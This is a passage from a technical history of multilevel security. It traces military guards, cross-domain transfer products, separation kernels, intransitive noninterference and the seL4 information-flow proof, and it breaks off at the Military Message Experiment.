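Rushby wrote that messages from the low system went up to the high system without hindrance, but Landwehr (1981), in *Best Available Technologies (BATs) for Computer Security*, described operators who monitored the requests as well as sanitizing the responses. The star-property doesn't require anyone to read a query on its way up, but operators may have done so because seeing the question helped them judge how much the answer gave away. The plans also assigned one sanitizing officer to each pair of databases, so that the officer would get to know their contents. Mail between the networks took a shorter route, in which the watch officer checked each message but nobody edited it.

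The kernel has to control the display in step 4 because an ordinary program could show the officer one text and forward another. The file level changer in KSOS locked a file during regrading for much the same reason. Before any message *m* reaches the low network, the Guard must display exactly *m* to the officer, and the officer must then approve *m*. The Bell–LaPadula model cannot express this condition on the order of events, just as it cannot express the KSOS rule on regrading.

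### Why the downgrader needed an exemption

KSOS allowed information to flow only upward, which was enough for half of the Guard's traffic, the queries from the Secret network. A process working at Secret can read a query and append it to a Top Secret queue, because Top Secret dominates Secret. A second process, working at Top Secret, can read the queue and pass the query to the database, and neither process needs an exemption from the star-property.

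On the way down, some process *d* has to read the approved reply R, which is still labelled Top Secret, and append it to the outgoing Secret buffer B:

b = {(d, R, read), (d, B, append)}.

As with the program that handled the convoy report, no current level permits both accesses. Relabelling R as Secret first would not help, because relabelling also requires a trusted subject. So *d* had to be a trusted process, and every reply the Guard released had to pass through it. Landwehr observed that virtually all applications need functions that violate the model.

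Even the upward path involves a small write-down if the sender wants to know that a query has arrived. The acknowledgement comes from a Top Secret process, and a hostile program could send information by choosing which acknowledgements to delay. The spooler's deletion of a printed file creates the same problem.

Rushby doubted that the kernel added much to the Guard's security, since the Guard's main function was to bypass it. The kernel was still useful for confining the programs that sanitize replies. These can run entirely at Top Secret, reading the original and writing a Top Secret draft, so the kernel can stop them from sending anything directly to the low network. Only the release step needs the exemption. Confinement reduces what a hostile sanitizing program can leak, but the program could still hide information in a draft that looks harmless, which the officer would then approve.

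The Guard also returned the release decision to a cleared person. In the paper system, such a person decided what to release, but under the exemption the spooler and the database server replaced that person with code. The Guard's trusted process had to do only three things correctly: display the true text, wait for a cleared officer's approval, and send what the officer had approved. This task was much narrower than a database server's and should have been a good candidate for proof.

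### The cost of verifying it

Logicon used Gypsy to specify the process that performed the downgrading. Gypsy was a language from the University of Texas for writing programs together with assertions about what they should do, and it came with tools for proving that a program met its assertions. Landwehr's tables list SPECIAL, the SRI specification language used for KSOS, as a second language for the Guard, but with a question mark.

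In July 1980 Landwehr reported that verification of the Guard's trusted processes had consumed "far more resources than originally planned", a remark that Rushby quotes. The tables of December 1981 still listed the verification as incomplete. Their entry for it is "(some)", where the brackets mark plans rather than accomplishments. Neither account shows where the effort went. The work may have taken more resources than planned partly because the verifiers, like those of KSOS, had no accepted model of a trusted process to start from.

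The designers had planned to run the Guard on the KSOS kernel's UNIX emulator, but the emulator performed poorly, and Ford Aerospace's contract ended in December 1980. The Navy then paid Logicon to find out whether the Guard could run directly on the kernel. In the meantime, a prototype ran on unmodified UNIX, which has no security levels to enforce. The prototype could show that the procedure worked for its operators, but it provided little evidence of whether a hostile program could bypass the watch officer.

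SCOMP, a Honeywell computer developed in parallel with KSOS, was the first to receive an A1 rating, the highest grade in the Defense Department's evaluation scheme. *Trusted software verification* is a case study of the verification of SCOMP's trusted software. Several earlier papers had discussed the verification of SCOMP's kernel, and the case study notes that most research and applications up to then had concentrated on kernels.

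### Three other designs of 1981

The LSI Guard was an attempt to provide the ACCAT Guard's functions without a kernel. I. P. Sharp Associates began building it for the Navy in 1980, as trusted processes running on the bare hardware of an LSI-11, a small computer from Digital Equipment Corporation. It allowed only one operator, whereas the ACCAT Guard could have several. Without a kernel to enforce the star-property, the guard needed no exemption from it. But nothing confined any of the software, so all of it belonged to the TCB. This tradeoff is reasonable if the whole program is small. The builders wrote it in Euclid, a language designed for verification, though the tables record no verification.

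The FORSCOM Guard stood between several terminals and a host computer of the World Wide Military Command and Control System. Logicon adapted it from the ACCAT Guard for the Army's Forces Command and built it on standard UNIX because KSOS was not available. A single operator screened the traffic for all the terminals. To reduce the operator's load, the program stored a good deal of information about what users of that host were likely to be doing. A stereotyped reply to an editing command, for example, could reveal little, while a reply to a database query might reveal a great deal. The other two guards stored no such information. The Army found the performance adequate for a trial, although some users complained.

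The Message Flow Modulator, which Don Good's group at the University of Texas developed for the Navy, had the simplest design. It receives messages from a source, discards some, transforms the others and sends the results to a destination. Let P be the test that a message must pass and T the transformation. Given inputs m₁, m₂, …, the device should output T(mᵢ) for exactly those mᵢ that satisfy P, in the original order. If T leaves messages unchanged, the device is a guard. If every message passes P and T encrypts, it is an ordinary encryption device.

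| System | Connects | Runs on | Who decides on release | Formal specification | Verification by late 1981 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| ACCAT Guard | Two databases or networks | KSOS (planned); UNIX for the prototype | Watch officer, with one or more operators | Downgrader, in Gypsy | Some planned |
| LSI Guard | Two databases or networks | Bare LSI-11 | One operator | Planned, in Euclid | None |
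| FORSCOM Guard | Several terminals and one host | Standard UNIX | One operator, helped by a filter | Planned, in Gypsy | Planned, in Gypsy |
| Message Flow Modulator | One source and one destination | LSI-11 | The program | In Gypsy | Some properties proved, in Gypsy |

Good's group had proved some properties of a simple modulator by the time Landwehr wrote, and was working on a version for a Navy system. Of the four, the modulator relied least on human judgement, which is partly why it had the most proof. The output condition above involves only P, T and the messages, so a verifier can compare the program with it line by line. But a proof that the program applies P correctly does not show that P is the right test. If P accepts a message that gives away a convoy's route, a fully verified modulator will send the route down every time. The ACCAT Guard left the decision about what to release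 to an officer, whose judgement nobody could verify.

### Release by rule

In 1981, MITRE was designing two guards with no operator, one for planning space shuttle flights and the other for the Korean Air Intelligence System. Each would connect a single terminal to a single host. Around the same time, a government committee considered three ways to build local networks for the worldwide command system. It received a recommendation for the most conservative, which was to keep a separate network for each level and connect them with a filter like the Guard. The US government still keeps separate networks for different levels of secrecy and connects them with products it calls cross-domain solutions.

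*Fundamentals of Cross Domain Solutions (CDS)* (Adam, 2024), a Defense Department briefing, divides cross domain products into three types. Access products, the most numerous, let a user on a high network operate a computer on a low one. Keystrokes and mouse movements go down, and a picture of the screen comes back up. Multilevel products store labelled data for users with different clearances. Transfer products, the modern guards, move data between networks and filter it on the way. Unlike a firewall, which usually connects networks of the same level and forwards packets that its rules allow, a transfer product forwards no packets. It accepts only a few kinds of traffic, such as e-mail and files, examines the contents and changes their classification.

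Many guards now release messages by rule, with no officer reading each one. Radiant Mercury, a US Navy guard, sanitizes and downgrades formatted messages this way. The SNS Mail Guard, which Smith (2014) describes, let each site define its release policy as a set of tests on message contents. Boeing sells a guard with an extensible rules engine for files and streaming data, and according to Boeing's *HardwareWall cross-domain data protection*, customers have deployed hundreds of them over more than twenty years.

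A rule-based guard is easiest to understand when messages have a fixed format, such as a ship position report with five fields: the ship's name, latitude, longitude, time and source. The guard first checks that the message has exactly these fields and that each holds a legal value, such as a latitude between −90 and 90 degrees. It then applies the release rules, which might delete the source, round the position to the nearest degree, or reject any report about a submarine. Finally, the guard builds a new message from the remaining values and sends that, so anything outside the expected fields is not passed on. If the message fails a test, the guard can reject it or refer it to a person.

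Guards now also check messages going from low to high networks. In Rushby's description of the ACCAT Guard, these messages pass unhindered, and the Bell–LaPadula model gives no reason to stop them, since it protects only secrecy. But a file from a low network can carry a virus, and *A High-assurance, Virtual Guard Architecture* (Heckman, Schell and Reed, 2012) describes scanning such files for viruses as a standard function of a guard. A virus that takes control of a program on the high network turns it into the kind of Trojan horse that the star-property was meant to contain.

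### One-way links

Some networks need traffic in only one direction, so hardware can do part of the guard's work. Bachicha, who leads work on transfer products at Sandia National Laboratories, names two methods, data diodes and "sneakernet" (carrying disks by hand). A data diode can be an optical fibre with only a transmitter at one end and only a receiver at the other, so no signal can travel backward.

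A data diode that points from low to high enforces the star-property physically, so no program needs an exemption and a software fault at either end cannot reverse the flow. *Multilevel Security*, a textbook chapter, gives the example of two databases joined by a "pump" that constantly copies the low one into the high one, so users on the high side have both sets of data without sending queries down. With a pure diode, the sender gets no confirmation that a message arrived, because an acknowledgement would have to travel down. Designers can compensate by sending everything more than once or adding error-correcting codes, and can accept that some messages will still be lost.

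A diode that points from high to low does not stop secrets from leaving the high network, so a filter still has to decide what goes through. The diode does block replies, so an attacker on the low network cannot use that link to send commands to a program on the high side or to learn how the filter responds to different inputs.

### Raise the Bar

Guards are attractive targets because they connect networks that an attacker could not otherwise move between. Adam lists threats from suppliers, insiders and the networks on both sides, as well as accidental release. The National Security Agency (NSA) responded with Raise the Bar, a set of requirements for the design, testing and use of cross-domain products. Green Hills Software, which supplies operating systems, dates the requirements to 2018. According to the responsible NSA office's web page, *National Cross Domain Strategy & Management Office*,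 they are intended to cover every product that protects classified US government information and every product sold for export. A White House memorandum of January 2022 required agencies to report their progress toward meeting them.

NSA distributes the requirements through Intelink, the intelligence community's own network, so the public knows them mainly from officials' briefings and suppliers' descriptions. Adam wrote in February 2024 that NSA revised them every year, and cited version 4.1, dated July 2022. *Learn About Cross Domain Solutions*, a guide from the supplier Owl Cyber Defense, describes the main design requirements. Filters must be redundant and independent of one another. The product must apply its security functions to every transfer, and it must be impossible to bypass them through the data stream, the hardware or the physical installation. Transfers between networks must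 be one-way and include a break in the communication protocol.

The protocol break stops a program on the high side from passing messages hidden in packet headers, which contain addresses, sequence numbers and other control information. The sending side of the guard ends the connection, extracts the content and discards the headers. The content crosses the one-way link, and the receiving side opens a new connection with its own headers.

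The rule about redundant filters addresses the weakness of relying on a single trusted process. Suppose a guard checks JPEG images with one filter, which has a bug that a specially built image can exploit. When the filter opens the image, the attacker's code takes control of the filter. If the filter also writes to the low network, the attacker can send anything the filter can read. In a redundant design, the first filter can pass its output only to a second filter, which runs in its own process and uses different code and a different supplier's JPEG library. To get anything out, the attacker needs an image that defeats the first filter and an output that the second accepts.

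If two filters miss a forbidden message with probabilities p₁ and p₂, and their misses are independent, both miss it with probability p₁p₂. Two filters that each miss one forbidden message in a thousand would then together miss one in a million. Real filters, however, may share causes of failure. If one tenth of each filter's misses come from a flaw in a library that both use, that flaw alone lets through one forbidden message in ten thousand, about a hundred times the independent figure. The requirements therefore include separate code. The calculation also assumes that errors occur at random, whereas an attacker who understands both filters will look for a message that both miss. Separate code reduces the number of such messages but does not guarantee that none exist.

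Redundancy also changes which components are trusted. A lone filter is trusted in the sense defined earlier, because its failure can break the policy. With two independent filters in series, one failure is not enough to break the policy, so the pair is trusted as a unit. The mechanism that forces every message through both is still trusted on its own, because a fault there would make the second filter useless. Redundancy also does not help with a mistake in the rules, such as a code name missing from the list of forbidden words, because two independently written filters that use the list will both let the name through.

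Because a message has to pass both filters, harmless messages get blocked more often. If each filter wrongly rejects 1% of them and the errors are independent, the pair rejects about 2%. Owl Cyber Defense's *A Brief Note on Raise the Bar and One-Way Transfer* predicted that Raise the Bar would make designs more complex, affect cost and performance, and lead some suppliers to leave the market. Owl sells such products, but Adam's figures are consistent with high costs: a new cross-domain product takes at least two to five years and millions of dollars to develop. New and modified products also have to go through security tests in a laboratory certified by NSA's office. The Air Force Research Laboratory (AFRL) tried to ease the problem with X-ARBITOR, a guard that combines a fixed, tested framework with exchangeable modules for inspecting and sanitizing data. AFRL (2021) presents the modules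 as a way to adapt quickly to new missions while still meeting the requirements. It reported that X-ARBITOR's laboratory assessment nevertheless took months, and that NSA included the architecture among a limited number of acceptable design patterns.

### The platform under the filters

A guard's filters run on an operating system, and a fault in that system can defeat them all at once. In January 2012, Heckman and colleagues found 28 entries on the government's list of available products, 19 of them transfer products. They judged, from what they called a cursory examination, that most of the guards ran on commodity systems with too little protection against deliberate tampering. They quote Bell, who by then thought it "unconscionable to use overly weak components" for connections between levels and wanted the A1 grade for all such connections.

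Their alternative runs on GEMSOS, the system that confines each exemption to a range of levels. The programs that handle network connections work at a single level and need no exemption. Only the downgrading program has a range, so if it were hostile, it could leak data only within that range. The same machine can therefore run several guards for different pairs of networks, and the kernel keeps them apart. The proposal comes from employees of the company that offers this design, so their view of competitors calls for caution, but the argument about ranges follows from the kernel's rules.

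*Security Anti-Pattern* (2008), a blog post, takes nearly the opposite position on platforms from Heckman and colleagues. It argues that government users built guards on Bell–LaPadula systems because the trusted operating systems of the time offered little else, and that the model suited guards poorly. The two positions can be reconciled because a kernel with strong evidence behind it protects the filters from tampering whatever policy it enforces, and Heckman and colleagues need that protection more than they need the star-property. Their kernel's only role in the release decision is to limit how far down a message can go.

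### What a rule can check

A rule can check anything that depends only on the symbols in a message, such as whether the fields are in the right order, a number is within its limits, a digital signature is valid, or a listed word occurs. Guards commonly search text for "dirty words", including the code names of secret operations. This search misses paraphrases, misspellings and new code names, and it may stop a harmless message that uses a listed word in its ordinary sense.

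Whether a message is secret usually depends on what it tells its reader, which may depend on facts outside the message. "The meeting has moved to Thursday" contains no forbidden word, but it could reveal the date of an attack to someone who knows what the meeting is about. Heckman and colleagues mention the US census, which publishes summaries soon after the count but must keep the raw returns from the public for 72 years. A rule that checks whether a file contains only totals must also anticipate cases such as a village with a single household, where the total is that household's return. Heckman and colleagues say that a person often has to review the results of word searches and sanitizing, because in many cases no algorithm can reliably establish that nothing sensitive remains.

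Fixed formats reduce the difficulty because designers can work out in advance what each field may reveal, so rule-based release is much more convincing for ship positions than for letters. Human review has weaknesses too. In a military message system from the ACCAT Guard's time, most users approved every transfer without thinking about it. The Australian Signals Directorate (2025) warns that technical solutions alone cannot solve every cross-domain problem and lists human factors among the other things to consider.

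Rules and reviewers are both poor at catching information that a program has deliberately hidden. A word-processor file may contain deleted text that the screen doesn't show, and a guard can remove it by converting the document to a plainer format. Hiding information in permitted values is harder to prevent. Suppose the time field in the ship report gives hours, minutes and seconds. A Trojan horse on the high network can set the seconds to any of 60 values without making the report look wrong, which conveys log₂ 60, or about 5.9 bits. At one report a minute, it can send about 8,500 bits a day, or roughly a thousand characters. Every message is well formed, contains no listed word and would look harmless to an officer, and even an independent second filter would accept it.

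The guard can close this channel by setting the seconds to zero. It would then have to close similar channels in the last digits of the position, the order of the reports and the times they are sent, and each change makes the reports less useful. Rushby discusses a similar problem in an encryption device that has to send some packet headers unencrypted. A small program called a censor checks that the headers look legitimate, and he claims only that a fairly simple censor can reduce the hidden traffic to an acceptable rate.

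Somebody then has to decide what rate is acceptable. Walker reports that one military user of the period would tolerate hidden channels about as fast as a teletype, assuming physical measures outside the computer could control them, but not channels as fast as a line printer. A teletype printed around ten characters a second, and the seconds field is far slower. Whether this is slow enough depends on the size of the secret. A Trojan horse using only the seconds field could send a 256-bit encryption key in 44 reports, in less than an hour.

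## Separation kernels, which replace the exemption with explicit channels

Rushby criticized the spooler and the ACCAT Guard as part of an argument that a security kernel should not enforce the star-property at all. The argument starts from the purpose of a kernel, which is to save people from having to examine the rest of the system.

Trusted processes undo this, because the kernel alone no longer controls where information may flow. Verification therefore has to cover the whole TCB, showing that trusted processes don't abuse their privileges and that untrusted programs can't take those privileges over. Rushby wrote that "we do not know what it is that we have to prove", because no model described what a kernel and its trusted processes had to achieve together.

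Nibaldi had proposed writing a second model for each trusted process. Rushby instead questioned the policy that made the exemptions necessary. A system may have to enforce the multilevel policy toward its users, but its components need not all obey that policy. One of Rushby's examples is the Guard, which needs a different rule for each direction. A system is only as secure as its weakest part, so Rushby saw no reason to build one component's requirements into the kernel and treat all the others as exceptions.

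### From separate machines to one machine

Rushby's alternative starts from a system with no kernel. Each user has a private computer with dedicated lines to a shared file server and a shared printer server, and no line joins two users. The printer server still has to delete spool files of every level, but it does so by sending a request to the file server. Designers can specify exactly what that request does, which is to delete a spool file and nothing else, whereas an exemption from the star-property would permit other actions too.

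The components still depend on one another, since both servers rely on whatever program checks users' identities. Rushby argued that a conventional system contains the same dependencies but makes them harder to see.

The example that best shows the difference is a device that encrypts a host computer's traffic before it enters a public network. The network's switches have to read each packet's header to know where to send it, so the device can encrypt only the body. It has a "red" side facing the host, a "black" side facing the network, and two paths between them:

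1. The red side receives a packet from the host and separates the header from the body.
2. It sends the body to an encryption unit, the crypto, which passes the encrypted version to the black side.
3. It sends the header along an unencrypted bypass, where a small program called the censor checks that it looks like legitimate protocol traffic.
4. The black side joins the header to the encrypted body and transmits the packet.

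The host's data must never reach the network unencrypted. The red software handles protocols and buffering, and Rushby considered it too large and complex to verify. The design therefore has to assume that this software may try to send data along the bypass. If each component has its own box, and the only wires are those of the two paths, the censor is the only software that security depends on. The crypto is also trusted, but it is hardware.

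Security levels describe this design poorly. If the host's data is Secret and the network is Unclassified, the crypto and the censor both read Secret data and write Unclassified data. Both therefore need an exemption, and it would allow far more than the one path each serves. When the components are separate boxes, the crypto and the censor each have one wire in and one wire out. Red must be able to influence black for the device to work, and the security requirement concerns which routes that influence can take.

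Separate hardware for every component is expensive. Military sites already kept security levels apart on a single machine by "periods processing", which Rushby (1981), in *Verification of Secure Systems*, describes as slow, inflexible and very costly. Operators ran the whole machine at one level for a time, then removed the disks and tapes, overwrote the fixed storage, and loaded a fresh operating system before starting the next level. This typically left less than 10% of the machine's normal throughput.

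A separation kernel is meant to provide the same isolation while the components share a processor. It gives each component a "regime", a virtual machine indistinguishable to the component from a dedicated computer, and it carries messages along the channels the designer has specified. The kernel does not use security levels. The censor needs no privilege from the kernel, because it does its job by reading from one channel and writing to another.

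The Royal Signals and Radar Establishment at Malvern, England, had already built a kernel of this kind for devices like the encryption unit. The Secure User Environment (SUE) ran on a PDP-11/34 minicomputer and occupied about 5,000 words of memory, including its data. Its designers kept it small by leaving out most of what a kernel usually does:

- Each regime permanently occupies a fixed part of memory, so SUE does not manage virtual memory.
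- SUE does no scheduling. A regime runs until it gives up the processor by calling an operation named SWAP, and the next regime then takes its turn. A regime that never calls SWAP stops the whole device, which Rushby treats as a problem of reliability and not of security.
- SUE bans direct memory access (DMA), which lets a device read and write memory without going through the protection hardware. Conventional kernels have to supervise all input and output for this reason. SUE can give each device permanently to one regime and leave that regime to run it.

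What remains is to switch between regimes, pass interrupts to the right one and operate the channels.

### Cutting the channels

A proof about the encryption device has to show that red can reach black only through the crypto and the censor. Proving that two regimes cannot communicate at all is easier than proving that they communicate only in permitted ways, so Rushby looked for a way to reduce the harder problem to the easier one. With physical boxes, one could cut the permitted wires and check that the boxes were isolated. Any remaining communication would have to use an illicit channel.

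In software, a channel is an object X that one regime writes and another reads. To cut the channel, the verifier replaces X with two new objects, using X₁ wherever the sender refers to X and X₂ wherever the receiver does. If the regimes are isolated in the altered system, X was the only channel between them in the original.

The next step is to prove the isolation. The established method, which KSOS had used, compares the levels of the variables that each operation reads and writes. It fails on SWAP, which saves red's registers and loads black's. SWAP leaks nothing, but the method cannot show this because SWAP handles values belonging to both. The method also leaves out interrupts, which are much of what a separation kernel deals with.

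Rushby's own method, proof of separability, compares each regime's view of the shared machine with an imaginary private machine. Let Φ be the function that takes a state s of the shared machine and returns the state of red's private machine. The proof has six conditions:

1. When the shared machine performs an operation op for red, red sees the effect of some operation op′ on its private machine: Φ(op(s)) = op′(Φ(s)).
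2. When the machine performs an operation for anyone else, red sees no change: Φ(op(s)) = Φ(s).
3. Input from red's devices changes red's view in a way that depends only on that input and red's existing view.
4. Input from other devices doesn't change red's view.
5. The output on red's devices depends only on red's view.
6. The choice of red's next operation depends only on red's view.

SWAP passes this test. Black's version of Φ takes the values of black's registers from the processor while black is running, and from the area where the kernel saved them while black is waiting. SWAP moves the values from one place to the other, so black's view stays the same.

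Rushby's *Proof of Separability* (1982) derives most of these conditions from a definition of isolation. The first definition required that what each user sees depend only on that user's input. This is too strong for a shared processor, because one user's activity affects how long another waits. Rushby therefore compared only the order in which outputs change, so the sequences 1, 1, 2, 2, 2, 3 and 1, 2, 3 count as the same. As a result, the proof doesn't cover timing channels. It doesn't cover denial of service either, because two runs count as equivalent even if one stops early. For input that arrives while the machine is running, Rushby proposed the conditions by analogy with the simpler case instead of deriving them.

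Rushby also admits in the 1982 paper that the method is specific to complete isolation, whereas most real systems need some communication. If red may send data to black with a WRITE operation, he suggests dropping condition 2 for that one combination. He calls this ad hoc, and it is again an exemption, now granted within the proof. Jeremy Jacob showed in 1989 that the technique of cutting the wires was subtly flawed, as Rushby later acknowledged, although the method for proving complete isolation survived with minor corrections. The approach still needed a definition of security that included the permitted channels.

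### Noninterference and why it forbids downgrading

Goguen and Meseguer published a promising candidate, noninterference, in 1982. One part of a system is *noninterfering* with another if nothing the first does affects what the second sees. Rushby's *Noninterference, Transitivity, and Channel-Control Security Policies* (1992) gives the definition in a convenient form. It divides the system into domains, such as High and Low, and assigns each action to one domain. The notation u ⇝ v means that the policy allows domain u to influence domain v. Every domain may influence itself.

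For a sequence of actions α and a domain v, let purge(α, v) be what remains of α after deleting every action whose domain is not allowed to influence v. The system is secure if, for every sequence α and every action a by v, a produces the same output after α as after purge(α, v). The deleted actions then have no effect on the outputs v receives.

Noninterference is defined by what users can observe, whereas Bell and LaPadula's definition concerns which accesses are open. A program that signals by deleting files violates noninterference if anyone at a lower level can see the result, even if the designers did not consider deletion a write.

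Rushby proved that the multilevel policies are exactly the transitive ones, those in which u ⇝ v and v ⇝ w always imply u ⇝ w. This explains why downgraders kept needing exemptions. A downgrader D has to receive information from High and send it to Low, but a transitive policy that permits both steps also permits High to send to Low directly.

An obvious remedy is to use a policy that is not transitive:

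High ⇝ D, D ⇝ Low, but not High ⇝ Low.

Goguen and Meseguer had suggested such policies for channels like those of the encryption device, but their definition doesn't work for these policies. Purging for Low deletes everything High did and must leave Low's outputs unchanged, so nothing from High may reach Low by any route. A system can meet this requirement only if D consists of two halves that never communicate, one receiving from High and the other sending to Low, and such a D cannot downgrade anything.

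### A trace through the downgrader

Haigh and Young gave the first satisfactory definition for intransitive policies in the mid-1980s, and Rushby adopted it. The purge should keep an action by High if a later action by D could have passed on its effects. The purge works backward through the sequence and maintains a set of *sources*, the domains from which information can still reach the observer. The set initially contains only the observer. If an action's domain is in the set or may influence a member of it, the purge keeps the action and adds its domain to the set. It removes all other actions.

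Take a machine with two memory cells, x and y, both initially 0. High can write to x. The downgrader's action d copies x into y, and Low's action outputs y. Suppose that the following happens:

- h₁: High sets x to 5.
- d: the downgrader copies x into y.
- h₂: High sets x to 9.

Low then looks at y and sees 5. The ordinary purge deletes both of High's actions and leaves only d, which copies the initial 0, so Low would see 0. Since 5 and 0 differ, ordinary noninterference classifies this machine as insecure, even though the information took the permitted route. The new purge gives a different result:

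| Action, working backward | May its domain influence a source? | Sources afterward | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| (start) | | Low | |
| h₂ | No, High may not influence Low | Low | Delete |
| d | Yes, D may influence Low | Low, D | Keep |
| h₁ | Yes, High may influence D | Low, D, High | Keep |

The purged sequence is h₁, d. Low sees 5 after it, as in the full run, so the machine passes this test. Now suppose a kernel fault makes each of High's actions write to y as well as x. Low then sees 9 after the full sequence but 5 after the purged one. This difference violates the definition, because h₂ reached Low without a later action by the downgrader.

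Nobody can check every possible sequence of actions, so Rushby proved an "unwinding theorem" that reduces the problem to checking single actions. The theorem has three conditions. An action must not change the view of any domain it is not allowed to influence. Any change it makes to a domain's view may depend only on that view and the view of the acting domain. Finally, a domain's outputs must depend only on its own view. Haigh and Young had an earlier unwinding theorem, but Rushby argued that it was probably false, and he had a computer check the proof of his own theorem.

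For a machine made of memory cells, the theorem leads to the rule that if u can alter a cell that v can observe, the policy must include u ⇝ v. In the example, High alters x, which D observes, and D alters y, which Low observes. High cannot alter any cell that Low can observe. The corresponding rule for ordinary noninterference also requires v to be able to observe everything u can, which would give Low access to x.

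Intransitive noninterference requires a downgrader's action to come between High and Low, but it does not require the downgrader to examine the information that passes. If d made the kernel copy a High cell hidden from d into y, that would satisfy the definition. The rule about cells excludes this case with the assumption that an action computes new values only from cells that its own domain may observe.

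### The seL4 proof

The KSOS proofs stopped at the kernel's specification, apart from a few illustrative proofs about the code. The commercial separation kernel INTEGRITY-178B later had a machine-checked proof of information flow, but that proof covered a handwritten model, and people checked only informally that the model matched the code. In 2013, Murray, Matichuk and colleagues published the first complete machine-checked proof of information flow for the code of a general-purpose kernel. Their paper, *seL4*, proves that the 8,830 lines of C in the seL4 microkernel enforce a variant of intransitive noninterference.

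Programs on seL4 can act only through capabilities. A capability is an unforgeable reference to an object and carries particular rights to it. When the system starts, one initial program holds all the authority. It creates the partitions (seL4's equivalent of regimes), gives each its capabilities, sets up the channels between them and then destroys itself. The theorem applies from that point on. The verifiers compute the policy from the capabilities. Under this policy, partition P may influence partition Q if P can affect anything that Q can learn about directly.

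The property they proved is called nonleakage. If two states of the system agree on the scheduler and on every partition that the policy allows to influence partition Q over the next n steps, then Q's contents must be the same in both cases after those n steps. seL4 runs the partitions on a fixed timetable that all of them may know, so the definition doesn't delete actions from a sequence to hide from Q that another partition has had its turn. Q must still not learn what that partition's memory contains.

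An earlier proof, which took about 25 person-years, had shown that the C code conforms to an abstract specification. Murray and colleagues could therefore prove nonleakage for the specification and carry the result over to the code. Their work took 51 person-months, 23 of them spent making the specification more definite. This was necessary because wherever the specification left open a choice that users could see, the C code might have based that choice on another partition's secrets.

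The proof also revealed unexpected channels. One came from ordinary deletion, as with the spooler. seL4 deletes an object when the last capability to it disappears, so a partition that discarded its own capability could find out whether another partition still held one. The remedy was to keep a spare copy of every capability that crosses a partition boundary, in a place no partition can reach, so that no partition ever deletes the last one. The kernel also reads the state of the receiving end when it delivers a one-way notification, so the verifiers had to show that none of this state becomes visible to the sender. They excluded seL4's synchronous messages from one-way channels because a sender that has to wait for the receiver learns something about it.

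The theorem assumes that the compiler, the linker, the hardware, the start-up code and 450 lines of assembly code work correctly, that the initial program configures the system properly, and that the system has one processor. All interrupts except the timer's must be off, so drivers have to keep checking their devices, and DMA must be off, as it was in SUE. Murray and colleagues also leave out most timing channels. For example, a partition can delay the start of the next one by making a system call just before its time runs out.

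Later work extended the proof to other processors. The seL4 Foundation's *Proof that seL4 enforces confidentiality established for RISC-V* announced a version for RISC-V, and by September 2026 the company Proofcraft had completed one for 64-bit Arm. According to Barry (2026), the Arm version needed new techniques because it includes virtual processors and floating-point units, whose contents sit in physical registers that may keep their values when the kernel switches programs.

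Some of the original assumptions remain. According to the seL4 Foundation's *Verified Configurations*, no verified configuration covers the kernel's start-up or the hardware that could make DMA safe by translating the addresses devices use. The Foundation's *seL4 News* describes a 2026 release that fixed problems in unverified configurations after an audit of code that the proofs don't cover. The AI company Anthropic had reported several of the problems.

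Timing channels are the largest remaining gap. If two partitions share a cache, the small fast memory that holds recently used data, one can learn which memory the other has used by timing its own accesses. Sison's *Where are we with Time Protection?* (2026) describes a defence in which the kernel divides the shared cache between partitions, clears the processor's other internal memory at each switch, and waits so that every switch takes the same time. The defence has passed experimental tests but has been difficult to verify. The first approach to verification recorded every memory address that the kernel touched, which broke more than 685 steps in seL4's existing proofs, on top of those the team had already repaired. Sison reports that a new approach has removed the main cause of the breakages. The plan is to prove complete isolation first and then one-way communication, which remains unproven.

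### What the censor lets through

Even a complete proof of this kind covers only the routes that information can take. In the trace above, d copied whatever High had put in x. If d instead checked the value and released it only if it was harmless, the policy, the purged sequence and the verdict would all be the same. The crypto in Rushby's device could pass plaintext through unchanged and still satisfy the policy. Rushby says in a footnote to the 1992 report that specifying what the crypto and the bypass must do is "a separate problem".

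For the censor, part of that specification can be a limit on how fast the red side can leak information through it. Suppose the censor forwards headers at fixed times and would accept any of n different headers each time. The red side can send one of these or none, which conveys at most log₂(n + 1) bits. If n is 4,095 and there are 50 opportunities a second, red can leak up to 600 bits a second. A stricter censor might check sequence numbers and lengths against earlier packets and leave only 15 acceptable headers each time, which reduces the limit to 200 bits a second. A verifier could prove such a limit from the censor's code, but the limit doesn't follow from any theorem about the kernel.

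Shared services need the same attention. *A Trusted Computing Base for Embedded Systems* (Rushby, 1984) illustrates this with an office where clerks of different clearances fetch folders from vaults. A filing clerk in the Unclassified vault fetches folders for visitors and keeps a directory of where each folder is stored. A Secret clerk, who may read anything in that vault, asks for the 5th, 14th, 9th, 7th, 13th and 1st smallest of its 26 folders. Read as letters of the alphabet, the numbers spell ENIGMA, and the filing clerk can write the word down for the next Unclassified visitor. Every request is a legal read, but the filing clerk can turn the requests into a message because he is allowed to keep records. Rushby concluded that programs managing shared resources generally have to be trusted, and defined the trusted computing base as the separation mechanism together with every domain that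 performs a trusted function.

Separation kernels therefore still have trusted components in the sense used here, but the kernel limits what each one can do. A faulty censor can leak only what red sends it, and only to black, whereas an exemption on KSOS covered every object the process had permission to open. The benefit is much smaller for a database server that reads all the data and answers all users, because it needs channels to every level and its own code controls what it sends through each one.

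The designer also has to choose the right channels. If a designer gives High a direct channel to Low by mistake, the policy that the verifiers compute from seL4's capabilities will include High ⇝ Low and the theorem will still hold, so somebody has to compare the computed policy with the intended one. Choosing channels resembles choosing S′ in the Bell–LaPadula model, but a diagram of components and channels is easier to check than a list of exempt programs because it shows where each program's output can go.

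The separation kernel at least divides verification clearly into two proofs. One shows that High can reach Low only through the censor, and the other shows what the censor passes. To join them formally, the proof about the censor must rely on an exact description of what the kernel's system calls do for the programs that use them. Sison writes in *Two interfaces for seL4 kernel verification* that the gap between kernel and user programs has long been "unbridged" for seL4.

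## Message systems in which a user authorizes the release

In the ACCAT Guard, a Security Watch Officer read other people's messages and decided whether to release them. In the same years, designers of military message systems tried to give that decision to the officers who wrote and sent the messages. Each officer would authorize downward transfers at an ordinary terminal, in the middle of other work.

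### The experiment at Camp Smith

In the late 1960s, long delays in delivering critical military messages worsened two crises involving American ships, the *Liberty* and the *Pueblo*, and Congress investigated. One eventual result was the Military Message Experiment, which the Navy and DARPA (formerly ARPA) ran from May 1977 to September 1979. At the headquarters of the Commander in Chief, Pacific, at Camp Smith in Hawaii, staff in the operations directorate used 25 terminals to read, file, draft and send military messages. One aim was to find out how multilevel security would affect its users.

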